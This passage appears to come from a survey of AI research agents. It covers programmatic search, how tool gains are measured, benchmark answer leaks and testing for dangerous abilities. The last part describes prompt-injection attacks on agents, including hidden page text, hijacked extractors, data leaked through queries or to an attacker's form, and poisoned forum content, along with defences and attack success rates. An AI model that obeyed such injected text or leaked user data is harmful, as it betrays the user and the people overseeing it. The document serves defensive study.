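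Qwen's trouble with separate calls probably came from a cluttered context. It found more of the relevant documents with separate calls than with the other two interfaces, but its context held an average of 175,000 tokens at the end of a run, compared with 74,000 when it wrote programs. All five models ended with the smallest context when they wrote programs, on average 34% smaller than with queries and 55% smaller than with separate calls. These figures don't measure the total cost of a run.

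On InfoSeek-Eval, an easier set of 300 questions, queries averaged 77.5%, separate calls 79.7% and programs 81.5%. The order was the same, but the programs' lead was smaller, at 4.0 points over queries and 1.8 over separate calls.

One run shows how the workspace helps. The question concerned a First World War battle and the commanders of two New Zealand forces. One program ran two searches and saved 20 merged passages, but returned detailed notes on only four. None of the four covered General Godley, one of the commanders. The next program picked three saved passages about Godley and extracted evidence from them without another search. A third looked for casualty figures, and the agent eventually gave the correct answer, the Battle of the Nek.

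A program that returns too little can lose useful passages before the agent sees them, just as a fixed extractor can. The researchers therefore tested GLM-5.3-Flash on 128 questions, once showing the model only what its program selected and once also showing it every passage the program had extracted. Selective output reduced the returned text by 37% and the final context from 36,900 tokens to 27,900. Accuracy was 3.9 points higher with selective output, but that is a difference of only five questions, so it is safest to conclude only that hiding most of the passages did no visible harm when the model could still go back to them in the workspace.

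Programs outperform queries only when the model has enough turns. In another test on 128 questions, the researchers limited Qwen3.8-Flash to between 10 and 50 turns. With 10 turns, it answered 35.16% correctly using programs and 39.06% using queries, a difference of five questions that is well within chance. With 30 turns or more, programs were ahead by 12 to 13 points, which is much harder to explain by chance. The query version hardly improved with extra turns, although its final context grew from about 32,000 tokens to 142,000. Qwen gained the most from programs in the main test, so other models would probably show a smaller gap.

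### OpenSAC on the live web

*OpenSAC* (Liu, Mao and colleagues, 2026) tested programmatic search on the live web. OpenSAC is an open-source Python library for existing coding agents, and it comes with written instructions on when to batch requests, save pages and return only excerpts. It uses reciprocal rank fusion to merge the results for different wordings of one query, and it keeps the results for separate questions apart. If one request in a batch fails, the program still receives the other results, with an error in place of the missing one.

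The researchers ran OpenAI's coding agent Codex with GPT-5.6 Luna twice on each task, once using its built-in web search and once using OpenSAC. They removed tasks with leaked answers and one faulty run, leaving 169 BrowseComp and 166 WideSearch tasks.

| | Built-in search | OpenSAC |
|---|---|---|
| BrowseComp, accuracy | 82.25% | 85.21% |
| BrowseComp, time per task | 473 s | 330 s |
| BrowseComp, model cost per task | $0.143 | $0.091 |
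| WideSearch, row F1 | 60.62% | 59.78% |
| WideSearch, time per task | 767 s | 540 s |
| WideSearch, model cost per task | $0.186 | $0.163 |

OpenSAC reduced token use by 38% on BrowseComp and 14% on WideSearch. Row F1 is the F1 score calculated over the rows of the table that the agent has to produce.

The accuracy gain on BrowseComp could easily be chance. Both setups got the same result on 146 of the 169 tasks. Of the other 23, OpenSAC alone answered 14 correctly and built-in search alone answered 9. If the two were equally good, each of these 23 tasks would be like a coin toss, and the probability of a split at least as uneven as 14 to 9, in either direction, would be

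p = 2 · [C(23, 14) + C(23, 15) + … + C(23, 23)] / 2²³ ≈ 0.40

where C(23, k) is the number of ways to choose k tasks out of 23. A split this uneven would therefore turn up in about two out of five such experiments even with no real difference. By the usual 5% standard, it would have taken at least 17 to 6 to count as evidence that OpenSAC was more accurate. The small decline on WideSearch deserves equally little weight.

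The time saving is more convincing because it was about 30% on both benchmarks. But the two setups also used different search services, and only one setup came with the written instructions. A faster search service could account for some of the difference. Running OpenSAC's search service through ordinary tool calls would separate the effects. The costs in the table exclude the search providers' charges.

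In one WideSearch task, the agent collected data with code, but the model still had to choose the right statistical series. The task was to find six monthly labour-market measures for four US states from January to June 2024. The agent's first program searched for suitable series in a batch. The model then examined the sources and chose two official databases. Later programs fetched the data in batches and converted the responses into a table of 24 rows, so the model never had to copy the monthly figures by hand.

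### When code saves money

Experiments on coding agents also suggest that the interface affects cost more than accuracy. Yang and colleagues restricted two agents, Claude Code and Codex, to a single tool that ran Python and shell commands and kept its state between calls. They compared this with the agents' normal tools and with a version that had a command line but no file-editing tools. The tasks were 93 computing problems and 100 repairs to existing software, with three runs each. The table shows the change in cost compared with the cheaper of the two alternatives:

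| Tasks | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| Computing problems | −24.6% | −6.7% (within chance) |
| Software repairs | +14.4% (within chance) | −19.9% |

Success rates differed by less than three points in every case. Codex saved money on repairs because one script could do the work of several calls and trim long outputs before returning them. Claude Code wrote 40% more tokens on repairs with the code tool, partly because it had to write a script for each edit instead of using its editing tool. Research agents rarely edit files, so the computing problems are more like their work.

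Anthropic's documentation also reports that calling tools from code cut billed input tokens by about 38% on a project-management benchmark with 75 tools, without changing accuracy. On a customer-service benchmark where each turn needed only one or two sequential calls, the same approach left scores unchanged and raised the cost by about 8%. Starting a sandbox and writing a script added to the cost, and with so few calls there was little to save. An agent that needs a single sales figure should search for it directly instead of writing a script.

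The program that surrounds the model can matter more than either interface. *The Scaffolding Matters More Than the Interface* (2026) compared several such programs on one software task, all using the command line. Claude Code used 28 times as many tokens as the leanest program, and Codex used 5.6 times as many. The Claude Code figure comes from only two runs, so the exact ratio is unreliable. Still, these differences are much larger than a 30% saving from a new search interface, so developers should keep the rest of the agent the same when they test a new interface.

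### Faults inside a search program

Programs add ways for a search to fail. In the test with different turn limits, 27 of the 640 runs with programs ended in an execution failure, compared with 1 of 640 with queries. Those failures were visible, but a filter that drops the right page is harder to notice. If the program keeps only pages with "heat pump" in the title, it drops a German statistics page titled "Wärmepumpen", and the model gets a shorter list with no sign that anything is missing.

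Printing a count after each step makes this easier to spot. From "Germany: 18 results, 0 after filter", the model can see that it needs to change the filter. If the program has saved the pages it fetched, as OpenSAC's instructions recommend, the agent can apply the new filter without repeating the search. Developers can also read the filter in the program and see exactly why it removed a page.

Code can also hide errors from the search service. Li warns that when an agent exceeds a search limit, the request to the model still counts as successful, and the error appears only in the output of the model's code. If that code skips failed searches without printing anything, the agent works with less evidence. This can lower a benchmark score without any error appearing in the developer's log, so Li recommends searching the transcripts for rate-limit messages and running fewer questions at once.

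Long loops can run out of time. The code tool in Li's setup gives the model the time limit for each program, so the model can split a large search into several shorter programs. This works best if each program saves its results as it runs. Otherwise, a loop that times out on the last of fifty pages may lose the results from the other forty-nine.

Text from the web also needs careful handling. Anthropic's documentation warns that a tool result may contain code or commands, which are dangerous if the program runs them instead of treating them as text. A program that reads sales figures from a page should convert them to numbers and reject anything else, and the sandbox should limit the damage if that check fails.

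## How much the tools add

A model with a search tool and a Python interpreter can find heat-pump sales figures and calculate with them, while the same model without tools must rely on its memory. Tool lift is the change in a model's score when it gets tools and everything else stays the same. The claim that tools multiply a model's abilities can mean several things, and different measures of tool lift can rank the same models in opposite orders.

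### Four measures

Suppose a model answers a share s₀ of the questions correctly without tools and a share s₁ with them. Three measures need only these two numbers:

- points gained: s₁ − s₀
- ratio of scores: s₁ / s₀
- share of errors removed: (s₁ − s₀) / (1 − s₀)

The fourth, compute-equivalent gain, is how many times more training compute the model would have needed to reach s₁ without tools. It comes from *AI capabilities can be significantly improved without expensive retraining* (Davidson, Denain and colleagues, 2023), which uses it as a common unit for comparing tools with other improvements made after the initial training, such as better prompts. The paper estimates from published results, without new experiments, that most of the improvements it surveyed were worth more than a fivefold increase in training compute, and some more than a twentyfold increase.

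Here are the first three measures for the models that Park and colleagues tested with and without tools on AgentHop, their benchmark of questions about linked papers:

| Model | Without tools | With tools | Points gained | Ratio | Errors removed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-chat | 18.3% | 56.4% | 38.1 | 3.1 | 47% |
| Gemma-4-31B | 31.7% | 64.8% | 33.1 | 2.0 | 48% |
| GPT-5.3 codex | 48.6% | 82.5% | 33.9 | 1.7 | 66% |

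DeepSeek-chat benefited most from tools, and GPT-5.3 codex least, when the gain is measured as the ratio of the score with tools to the score without. The order is reversed when the gain is measured by errors removed. The ratio tends to be higher for models that start with low scores, and DeepSeek-chat started below the 25% expected from guessing. Its score with tools is only 2.3 times that 25%.

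The ratio of scores with and without tools is least useful when the score without tools is close to zero. In Iordache's code-breaking test, Python raised the success rate by 38 points, about the same as DeepSeek-chat's gain, but the ratio was 8.3 because the models had solved almost nothing without it. For someone relying on the answers, the share of errors removed is usually more informative. Tools cut GPT-5.3 codex's wrong answers from 51 in a hundred to about 18, a reduction of nearly two-thirds.

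Compute-equivalent gain needs more information, namely how fast scores without tools rise with training compute. If they rise by d points for every tenfold increase, then

compute-equivalent gain = 10^((s₁ − s₀) / d)

with both scores in percentage points. A lift of 8 points is worth about 40 times the compute if d is 5, but only about 6 times if d is 10. Small errors in d therefore change the result enormously, and developers rarely publish the compute figures needed to estimate it. The measure also breaks down for facts that appeared after training ended, because no amount of extra training on older text would supply them.

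A cruder comparison avoids this problem. DeepSeek-chat with tools scored higher than GPT-5.3 codex without them, although codex was far ahead when both models had the same tools or none. So on this benchmark, tools made up for the difference between a weaker and a stronger model.

### Do search and code multiply?

If search doubles a model's score and code raises it by half, having both might triple it, or the two gains might add up. To find out, researchers would have to use a factorial design, testing the same model without tools, with search only, with code only, and with both. If the first three scores were 20%, 40% and 30%, the model would score 50% with both tools if the gains add, and 60% if they multiply.

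The interaction between the tools is

I = s(both) − s(search) − s(code) + s(neither)

which is zero in the first case and 10 points in the second. The formula has a simple meaning if we assume that a tool never spoils an answer the model would otherwise have got right. Questions that the model can answer without tools cancel out, and so do questions that need one particular tool. That leaves

I = (share of questions that need both tools) − (share that either tool could solve alone)

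An agent might need both search and code execution to calculate average growth across fifty regions, since it has to find a large table and then calculate with it. It needs only one of these tools to find the thousandth prime number, which it can either look up or compute. Whether the two tools together add more than the sum of their separate gains therefore depends heavily on the benchmark's questions, and a single figure wouldn't apply to all research tasks.

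The interaction is also harder to measure than a single score. With 500 questions, scores near 50% and independent runs, each score has a standard error of about 2.2 points. The interaction's standard error is about 4.5 points, so it would have to be around 9 points to be clearly distinguishable from chance. Using the same questions in all four tests reduces this noise, because an unusually hard question lowers every score.

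Studies that test an agent with search alone, code alone, both and neither are hard to find. Park and colleagues' AgentHop runs with and without keyword search show what it adds for an agent that can already follow references, but not what it would add on its own. If keyword search and reference lists can each find most of the papers, removing either one will make little difference, while removing both could leave the agent unable to find most of them. Testing every combination of five tools would take 32 versions of the agent, so researchers usually remove one tool at a time, even though this can miss such overlap.

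### Humanity's Last Exam with and without tools

Anthropic tests its models on Humanity's Last Exam both ways. The summary page *Humanity’s Last Exam* describes the two setups for Claude Mythos Preview. Without tools, the model could only reason. With tools, it could search the web, fetch pages, run code and call its other tools from code. These are the scores for three Anthropic models from 2026:

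| Model | Without tools | With tools | Points gained | Errors removed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 49.8% | 57.9% | 8.1 | 16% |
| Claude Mythos Preview | 56.8% | 64.7% | 7.9 | 18% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 59.0% | 64.5% | 5.5 | 13% |

On Humanity's Last Exam, tools removed less than a fifth of the errors in each case, a modest gain compared with AgentHop. Many of the exam's questions require expert reasoning that a search can't replace, whereas AgentHop's questions are about details in particular papers, so a model that opens the right paper has most of what it needs.

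Claude Mythos 5, one of the two models in Anthropic's *System Card* (June 2026), scored about 2 points higher than Mythos Preview without tools and almost the same with them. A stronger model may already know more of what it would otherwise look up, so tools can add less as a model improves. But the two models' gains from tools differ by only 2.4 points, which could be due to chance or small changes in the setup.

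The newer Claude Fable 5.2 scored 74.2% with tools, according to Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026). That is almost 10 points above Mythos 5, but the score alone doesn't show how much the tools contributed. If tools added between 5.5 and 8.1 points, as they did for the three earlier models, Fable 5.2 would score between 66% and 69% without them. Most of its improvement would then have come from the model, though Fable 5.2 may instead be better at using its tools.

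Code seems to help much more with documents. GDP.pdf is a set of 100 tasks with real PDF files. *Claude Fable 5 and Mythos 5*, by thezvi, reports that Claude Fable 5 scored 72.7% on it with an internal setup and 87.6% when it also had Python tools, which cut errors by 55%. Python also helped every model on BenchCAD.

### Memory or evidence

A model with tools may score well because it already knew many of the answers, so a high score doesn't prove that it is good at research. *REDSearcher* (2026), which describes an open search agent with 30 billion parameters, compares several systems with and without tools. Without tools, the agent scored lowest, while several strong competitors answered a fair number of questions from memory. The agent improved substantially with tools. The developers argue that this gain is a better sign of search ability than the final score, since the competitors may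 have seen some of the benchmark material in training.

Tool lift, the number of points that tools add to an agent's score, has some merit as a measure, but it also favors models that know less. If two agents both score 60% with tools, but one scores 10% without them and the other 40%, the first has a lift of 50 points and the second only 20, even if they search equally well. A developer could raise an agent's lift by removing knowledge from its model that the agent can look up.

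The choice of questions can have the same effect. REDSearcher's developers generated practice questions and discarded any that a model could answer without tools. They also rewrote facts so that the agent had to use a tool, for example by describing a city as about two hours' drive west of another place. This is sensible for training, but on a benchmark built the same way, scores without tools would be close to zero, and nearly every correct answer would count as tool lift.

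AgentHop provides a more direct check by recording whether a run opened every paper that contains part of the answer. We calculate from Park and colleagues' figures that GPT-5.3 codex opened all the necessary papers and answered correctly on about 65.5% of the questions. Its total score was 82.5%, so about 17 percentage points, a fifth of its correct answers, came from runs in which it had not opened at least one of those papers. It may have known those answers, inferred them from abstracts or guessed. For DeepSeek-chat, such runs contributed only about 7 points.

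### What more calls add

A tool score also depends on how long the agent may keep using its tools. Many agents stop when their context window is full. REDSearcher uses a simple remedy called discard-all: once the history reaches a set limit, the software deletes all earlier thoughts, calls and results, and the agent starts again with the question. This makes room for more calls. REDSearcher's developers report scores on BrowseComp with and without context management for their own agent and four larger open ones:

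| Agent | One context | With context management | Points gained |
|---|---|---|---|
| REDSearcher | 42.1% | 57.4% | 15.3 |
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 51.4% | 67.6% | 16.2 |
| GLM-4.7 | 52.0% | 66.6% | 14.6 |
| LongCat-Flash-Thinking | 56.6% | 73.1% | 16.5 |
| Kimi-K2.5 | 60.6% | 74.9% | 14.3 |

The five gains are very similar, and each is larger than the total gain from tools for any Claude model in the Humanity's Last Exam table. A benchmark score with tools is therefore hard to interpret without knowing the limits on tool calls and context.

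Not all of this gain necessarily comes from longer investigations. An agent that deletes its history and starts again is making a second attempt, and second attempts help even when they are no longer than the first. The *Tongyi DeepResearch Technical Report* gives a sense of how much. Its agent answered 43.4% of BrowseComp questions correctly on average, but it answered 59.6% correctly at least once in three attempts. If every question had the same 43.4% chance of success each time, three attempts would have been enough for

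1 − (1 − 0.434)³ = 82%

of them. The actual figure is much lower because some questions are easy for the agent every time and others defeat it every time.

An agent that makes several attempts at a question also has to recognise which one is right. Tongyi's "heavy mode" runs several agents in parallel and has a model write one answer from their final reports. In 2025, it scored 58.3% on BrowseComp, nearly the share of questions that the ordinary agent got right at least once in three attempts. It also raised the score on Humanity's Last Exam from 32.9% to 38.3%. Claude Mythos 5 has since scored 88.0% on BrowseComp as a single agent and 93.3% as a group of agents, so more agents still help, though there is much less room for improvement.

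More tool calls don't always improve research. During the last stage of REDSearcher's training, average tool calls fell from 100.6 to 90.1, while its BrowseComp score rose from 39.4% to 42.1%. A version of REDSearcher that also handles images sometimes kept searching after it had found the right evidence, apparently because its confidence was too low to answer. On AgentHop, DeepSeek-chat used more than twice as many tokens per question as GPT-5.3 codex and answered far fewer questions correctly. A higher call limit helps an agent that reaches the limit before finishing, but a better agent may need fewer calls.

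### When tools lower the score

Sometimes a model does worse with tools. The model in ReAct was slightly less accurate when it could consult Wikipedia, and GPT-5.4 lost 8.4 points on olympiad problems when it could run code. On AgentHop, four of the 19 models scored below 25% with all seven tools, which is worse than guessing. This doesn't prove that the tools lowered their scores, because DeepSeek-chat scored below 25% without tools.

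One of the four, Gemma-4-26B-A4B, reached a limit before answering in 44% of its runs, usually the token limit, and all of those runs counted as wrong. It scored 23.6% overall and about 42% in the runs it finished. If the software had made it guess before it reached a limit, it would have gained around 11 points. Gemini-3 Flash, a much stronger model, also reached a limit before answering in 30% of its runs. It scored 54.7% overall and about 78% in the runs it finished, although the questions in those runs were probably easier.

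Two other models stopped researching too early. Qwen3-32B opened no paper sections in 45% of its runs, and Gemma-3-27B opened none in 29%. When either model read a paper that didn't contain the answer, it submitted an answer immediately more than 60% of the time. One of the three wrong options for each question comes from the starting paper, so a model that reads only that paper may find text that seems to support that option, and could do worse than if it had read nothing.

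Weak models need more than access to tools. The share of runs in which the larger conventional models found the necessary papers rose roughly five- or sixfold from Gemma 3 to Gemma 4 and from Qwen 3 to Qwen 3.5. The tools were the same, so the improvement came from the models.

### What inflates tool lift

The most common problem is that the systems being compared differ in more than their tools. The *Tongyi DeepResearch Technical Report* compares its agent with a base model without tools on two mathematics competitions and on SimpleQA, a set of short factual questions. The agent did much better, and the developers credit search for the factual questions and Python for the mathematics. But the agent also had extensive training that the base model lacked, so the comparison can't separate the effect of the tools from that of the training. To do that, the developers would also need to test the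 base model with tools and the trained agent without them.

Training alone can make a large difference. The agent that Zhu and colleagues trained in *DEEPRUBRIC* scored 28.8 points higher on scientific questions than the original model, although both could search. Training could easily explain part of Tongyi's improvement too.

A model with tools is often also allowed to reason for longer. In AgentHop, a model without tools had to answer in a single turn, while an agent could take 20 turns and use 200,000 tokens. With tools, Claude Mythos Preview could use up to 3 million tokens on each question in Humanity's Last Exam, and software condensed its context every 50,000 tokens. Some of the extra tokens are search results, but others are the model's own reasoning. A fairer test would let the model without tools use as many reasoning tokens as the agent does.

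### Answers on the web

Search can also lead an agent to a benchmark's answers. Researchers publish benchmark questions and answers online, and other people discuss them, so an agent that searches for the wording of a question may find its solution. In the OpenSAC experiment, Liu and colleagues checked the saved runs for such cases. They excluded 31 of 200 BrowseComp tasks and 33 of 200 WideSearch tasks, about one in six overall, because answer material had reached the agent in at least one of the two setups.

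A simple formula shows how much this could matter. If an agent would honestly answer a share a of the questions correctly, but finds and copies the answers to a share ℓ of them, its score rises by

ℓ(1 − a)

provided that the leaked questions are of average difficulty. With ℓ at 15.5%, as in BrowseComp, an agent that deserves 40% would score 49.3%. An agent that deserves 82% would gain less than 3 points, because it would have answered most of the leaked questions anyway. These are upper estimates for OpenSAC, since some answers may have leaked in only one setup and the agent may not have used every answer it saw.

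Evaluators can exclude leaked tasks or count them as wrong. Anthropic did the latter for Humanity's Last Exam. It blocked sources known to discuss the benchmark in both its search and page-fetching tools. Claude Opus 4.6 then reviewed every transcript for answers from such sources, and any confirmed case counted as wrong. This policy gives no credit for copying, but it penalises a model for questions that it might have solved by itself. If 15.5% of the answers had leaked and all of them counted as wrong, an agent that deserved 82% would score only 69%. When there are few leaks, the two policies give similar scores.

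Reviewers can also miss leaked answers when an agent uses an extractor or searches from inside a program. The transcript may contain only a short extract with the right answer, with no sign that it came from an answer key. To check for these leaks, reviewers need the address and full text of every page the software fetched. A fixed collection such as the one in BrowseComp-Plus prevents leaks from the live web, provided nobody has put the answer key in it, but it can't show how well an agent copes with the real web.

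When test answers leak into a model's training data, the model scores higher without tools, so the tools have less to add and the lift shrinks. Two models can therefore have different lifts because one saw the answers during training and the other found them by searching.

### Testing for dangerous abilities

Developers test whether new models could help people carry out attacks or build weapons, and they base their safeguards partly on the results. If they test a model without the tools its users will have, they may underestimate what it can do. Suppose a developer had to add safeguards to any model that scored above 50% on a test of dangerous knowledge, and that models scored about as they do on AgentHop. DeepSeek-chat, Gemma-4-31B and GPT-5.3 codex would all exceed the threshold only with tools.

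Tests without tools may still rank models fairly well. Park and colleagues found that AgentHop scores had a rank correlation of 0.72 with scores on Humanity's Last Exam without tools, and 0.67 with tools. These figures cover only 14 and 10 models respectively, so the difference means little. But a safety threshold concerns how much a model can do, which even a correct ranking doesn't show.

Anthropic's *System Card* (September 2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 includes tests of the model as an agent, one of which measured how well it could plan and run a simulated covert influence operation. Anthropic used a "helpful-only" version with reduced safety training, because refusals could otherwise hide what the model was able to do. This version did better than Claude Opus 5 but slightly worse than Claude Mythos 5.1. Missing tools can also hide an ability, so it makes sense to supply them in such tests.

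The card also concludes that Opus 5.5 could help with making known chemical or biological weapons but not with developing new ones. Anthropic reasons that certain weaknesses limit how far the model can replace scarce human experts. A conclusion like this depends on the test conditions, because search might fill a gap in knowledge but probably won't fix poor judgement about which experiment to try. Testing the same model with and without search would help to distinguish these two kinds of weakness.

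The limits on a test matter as much as the list of tools. Context management alone added about 15 points to the BrowseComp scores of five agents, so a safety test that stops when the context first fills up could miss a similar gain. Nearly half of Gemma-4-26B-A4B's runs reached a limit, so an evaluator who saw only its score of 23.6% might conclude that it couldn't do the task at all. For a safety test, it would be better to raise the limits until the score stops improving, or at least to report how many runs ended without an answer.

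Counting every leaked answer as wrong can only lower a model's score. This is cautious when a company is advertising the model's abilities, but in a test for dangerous abilities, a score that is too low is the more serious error. Evaluators running such tests should exclude or replace leaked questions. They should also avoid blocking whole websites that contain useful technical information along with the answers, since a person misusing the model could still reach those sites.

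Even thorough tests before release can become outdated. Davidson and colleagues found that improvements after training typically cost less than 1% of what the original training cost, so many people can afford to make them. Anyone with a copy of an open model can connect it to a better search engine, allow it more calls or add a specialised code library. The developer may not be able to tell, so it would be prudent to leave a margin below the safety threshold and repeat the tests when much better tools appear.

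## Hidden instructions in search results and pages

Web pages can contain text written to control the agents that read them. Researchers call it prompt injection when a model treats such text as an instruction, although no authorised person gave it. On the heat-pump question, a manufacturer's page might contain a hidden request to favour the manufacturer's sales figures, and the agent could comply without the user noticing. *PISmith* (2026), a paper on automated attacks, credits Willison with first identifying the weakness in 2022, in applications built on GPT-3.

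### One stream of text

A model receives the developer's instructions, the user's question and every observation as one sequence of tokens. Markers show where each part begins, but the model learns to treat the parts differently only through training, and it learns this imperfectly. Willison showed in 2023 that putting such markers around untrusted text doesn't reliably stop injection.

*PIPETTE* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) formally describes injection as one altered observation that contaminates the history for every later step. A hostile instruction on an early page can therefore change a search many turns later. An agent that discards its history, like the one in *IterResearch*, also loses the instruction, unless it has copied it into its running report.

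A rule against acting on anything in a page would make research impossible. If a note on a statistics page gives an annex as the location of the revised figures, a good agent opens the annex. The model has to distinguish such notes from hostile commands, and the two can look alike.

Models seem to rely partly on writing style to tell the user's words from other text. *AutoPI* (Damianakis and Psounis, 2026) cites research on models' internal activity which found that models represent injected text in a user's style as the user's own words, even inside the markers for tool output. This confusion also predicted whether attacks succeeded.

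Stopping at the first suspicious line isn't a good solution either. It defeats the attack, but the agent needs the rest of the page to answer the user's question. A model can decline when a user asks for something harmful, but here the user's question is innocent.

### Hostile text in each tool

| Tool | Where the text can be | What it could change |
|---|---|---|
| Web search | Title, snippet or address | Which pages the agent opens and what it searches for next |
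| Scholarly search | Title or abstract, for instance of a preprint | Which studies the agent cites and how it describes them |
| Page reader | Anywhere on the page, including text that people can't see | The extract, and through it the answer or a later tool call |
| Python interpreter | A downloaded file, or text that a program prints | The next program, or the files it reads and writes |

A search result's address alone can mislead an agent. *MalURLBench*, by Kong, Wu and colleagues, contains 61,845 test cases built around disguised malicious addresses that an agent might accept as safe.

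Search queries and page addresses also leave the agent's software, so a hijacked agent can leak information even if it has no tool for sending messages. If the user has uploaded a confidential report, part of it could end up in a query or in the address of a page on the attacker's server. The damage depends on what the agent is permitted to do. *Depth-Dependent Indirect Prompt Injection in Tool-Calling ReAct Agents* (2026) counts web search as an action, alongside sending email and deleting files. In its tests, an attack succeeds if the attacker's chosen text appears in the arguments of any such call. The study has only 20 scenarios, so each one changes the success rate by five percentage points.

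A file is less dangerous when a program only converts its cells to numbers. If the program prints a column of text, any command in that column reaches the model as an observation. Programmatic search gives some protection by accident because the model sees only what its program returns.

Users can't easily spot these attacks by checking the sources. *Security of Deep Research Agents* (2026), a survey, cites a large study of real web pages in which most injected text was invisible to human readers. It also warns that attackers can recognise requests from an agent's page reader and send it a different page from the one people see. A reviewer who opens the citation would then find nothing wrong. The saved text of the page the software fetched is much better evidence.

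Attackers already use hidden text on live websites. Mascellino (2026) reports in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* that the security company Zscaler found sites that tried to manipulate agents into making cryptocurrency payments. A research agent without a payment tool couldn't make such payments, but similar text could still alter its answer.

### Malicious results from search services

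*Every Major Search API Fed AI Coding Agents Malicious Content, Benchmark Finds* (Faisal, 2026) describes the results of the WebSec Benchmark, which estimates how often search services return malicious content. The testers sent 4,719 programming queries to eight services, including Brave, Perplexity and You.com, and examined about 282,000 results. Every service returned content already known to be malicious, in 0.8% to 2.2% of searches.

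AIR Research Lab, the research arm of AIR Security, published the benchmark. AIR Security sells a firewall for AI agents and launched publicly with $50 million in funding, according to *AI Agent Firewall Startup AIR Security Emerges From Stealth With $50 Million* (Townsend, 2026). The company stands to gain if developers think search results are dangerous, and it hasn't released its queries or scanner, so outsiders can't check the figures.

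The figures are at least consistent with each other. If every query went to all eight services, there were 37,752 searches, and the 534 that returned known malicious content are 1.4% of them. At that rate, an agent that ran 50 independent searches would have about a 50% chance of getting at least one known malicious result.

For most research questions, the risk of prompt injection is probably much lower. Besides prompt injection, the benchmark counts fake software packages and abandoned domains that attackers have bought and filled with malicious content. Programming queries attract such attacks because a coding agent may install what it finds. AIR also wrote plausible queries to fit the 850 recorded coding sessions with the most searching, so the queries weren't a random sample of agents' searches.

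### The extractor as a filter and a target

A page reader's extractor can protect the main agent, because only the extractor reads the hostile page. But the extractor is also a language model, so a page can hijack it too. The harm depends on what the extractor can do and what it can send back to the agent.

Brave's *Indirect Prompt Injection remains a fundamental security challenge for AI* describes an extractor with too much power. Brave's researchers asked Mozilla Tabstack, a cloud service, to summarise a web page. Hidden instructions on the page redirected the service to a form controlled by the attacker, where it entered the conversation history and submitted it. Brave competes with Mozilla in browsers, so it has an interest in publicising the case. Still, a service that only has to summarise a page doesn't need to submit forms or see the conversation.

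Taking away the extractor's tools prevents this, but its output can still carry an attack. Tongyi's extractor returns two free-text fields, `evidence` and `summary`. The `evidence` field is meant to preserve the original wording, so it can pass on a hostile command unchanged. The `summary` field may be worse, because the extractor could turn the command into a polite recommendation next to genuine findings, without the odd position or formatting that might make it look suspicious on the web page. The agent would then receive it from a component it normally relies on. Extractors that copy numbered blocks from a page can't reword a command, but they can still select the block that contains it.

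Fixed fields are much safer. For one country's heat-pump sales in one year, the software could accept only these values:

| Field | Allowed values |
|---|---|
| Year | 2021 or 2024 |
| Units sold | A whole number below 10 million |
| Includes air conditioners | Yes, no or not stated |

This leaves 2 × 10,000,000 × 3 = 60 million possible outputs, which is about 26 bits of information, or little more than three characters of ordinary text. A hijacked extractor can't fit an instruction into that. The software has to enforce the limits itself and reject everything else, because an attacker can try to override an instruction telling the extractor to use only these fields. Adding a "notes" field for footnotes would let hostile text through again.

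### A privileged and a quarantined model

Developers can extend this separation to the whole agent by using two models. The privileged model sees the user's question and can call tools, but it never reads text from the web. The quarantined model reads that text but has no tools. For the heat-pump question, they could work together like this:

1. The privileged model writes a program that lists the searches, the fields to extract and the calculation.
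2. The software runs the searches and gives each page to the quarantined model.
3. The quarantined model fills in the fields, and the software checks their form and stores them under names such as `sales_A_2024`.
4. The program calculates with the stored values, and the software inserts the results into the answer.

An instruction on a page to visit another site or send an email now has no effect on which actions the agent takes. The command may influence the quarantined model, but that model can't carry it out, and the privileged model never receives it. This protection doesn't depend on recognising the attack, so rewording the command doesn't help the attacker.

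The design doesn't ensure that the extracted content is true. In the invented figures used earlier, country C sold 190,000 heat pumps in 2024 and ranked fourth, with a rise of 0.47 units per thousand people. If a hostile page made the quarantined model report 600,000, the rise would be 5.38 and country C would rank first, both in units per thousand people and in percentage growth. The false number fits its field and would also pass the earlier range check of 0.1 to 50 units. Probably only a comparison with another source would expose it.

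An attacker can do this without a hidden command. *Deep-Research Agents Can Be Poisoned via User-Generated Content* (2026) tested agents that rely on sites such as Reddit and Wikipedia. When the researchers poisoned an entire Reddit forum, the agents' reports cited the poisoned content 30% to 53% of the time, although it made up 0.5% to 4% of what the agents retrieved. Separating the models wouldn't stop this, because the pages contain false claims rather than instructions.

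Protection is only partial when text from a page goes into a later tool call. For example, to find who founded the company that makes Poland's best-selling heat pump, the privileged model can specify in advance a search for the founder of whatever company the extractor returns. The next action will then certainly be a search, but the page can influence its wording. The software could limit this by accepting only company names from an existing list.

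Strict separation also makes research less flexible. In the medical case from *AgentFrontier*, the agent searched for bone infection because of what it had read in its first results. A privileged model that never read those results couldn't have chosen that search unless someone had anticipated the possibility and created a field for it. Separation therefore suits the sales figures better than the studies' conclusions about subsidies. For the studies, the main model may have to read the text, and it would be sensible to remove its access to private files while it does.

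### Success rates in 2026

The attack success rate is the share of attacks in which the agent does what the attacker wanted. Some tests measure it per attempt, while others measure the share of scenarios in which at least one of several attempts succeeds, which is always at least as high.

*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports on a public competition in which 464 people made 272,000 indirect prompt injection attempts against 13 models. Of these, 8,648 (3.2%) succeeded. The success rate ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Some attack strategies worked on 21 of the 41 target behaviours and on several families of models, which suggests that the models share a weakness.

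Gray Swan, the security company that runs these competitions, also reuses the attacks as a benchmark. The September system card for Claude Fable 5.1, from Anthropic, gives results for 1,804 attacks in 37 scenarios. These are the chances that an attacker succeeds within a given number of attempts:

| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
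| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |

Gemini 3.7 Flash, the best model from another company, had an attack success rate of 9.2% after 15 attempts, and most of the others were between 24% and 53%. Nearly all successful attacks on Fable 5.1 occurred when it controlled a computer through its graphical interface, where the rate was 4.1% after 15 attempts. None succeeded in the tool-use scenarios, which are closest to a research agent's work.

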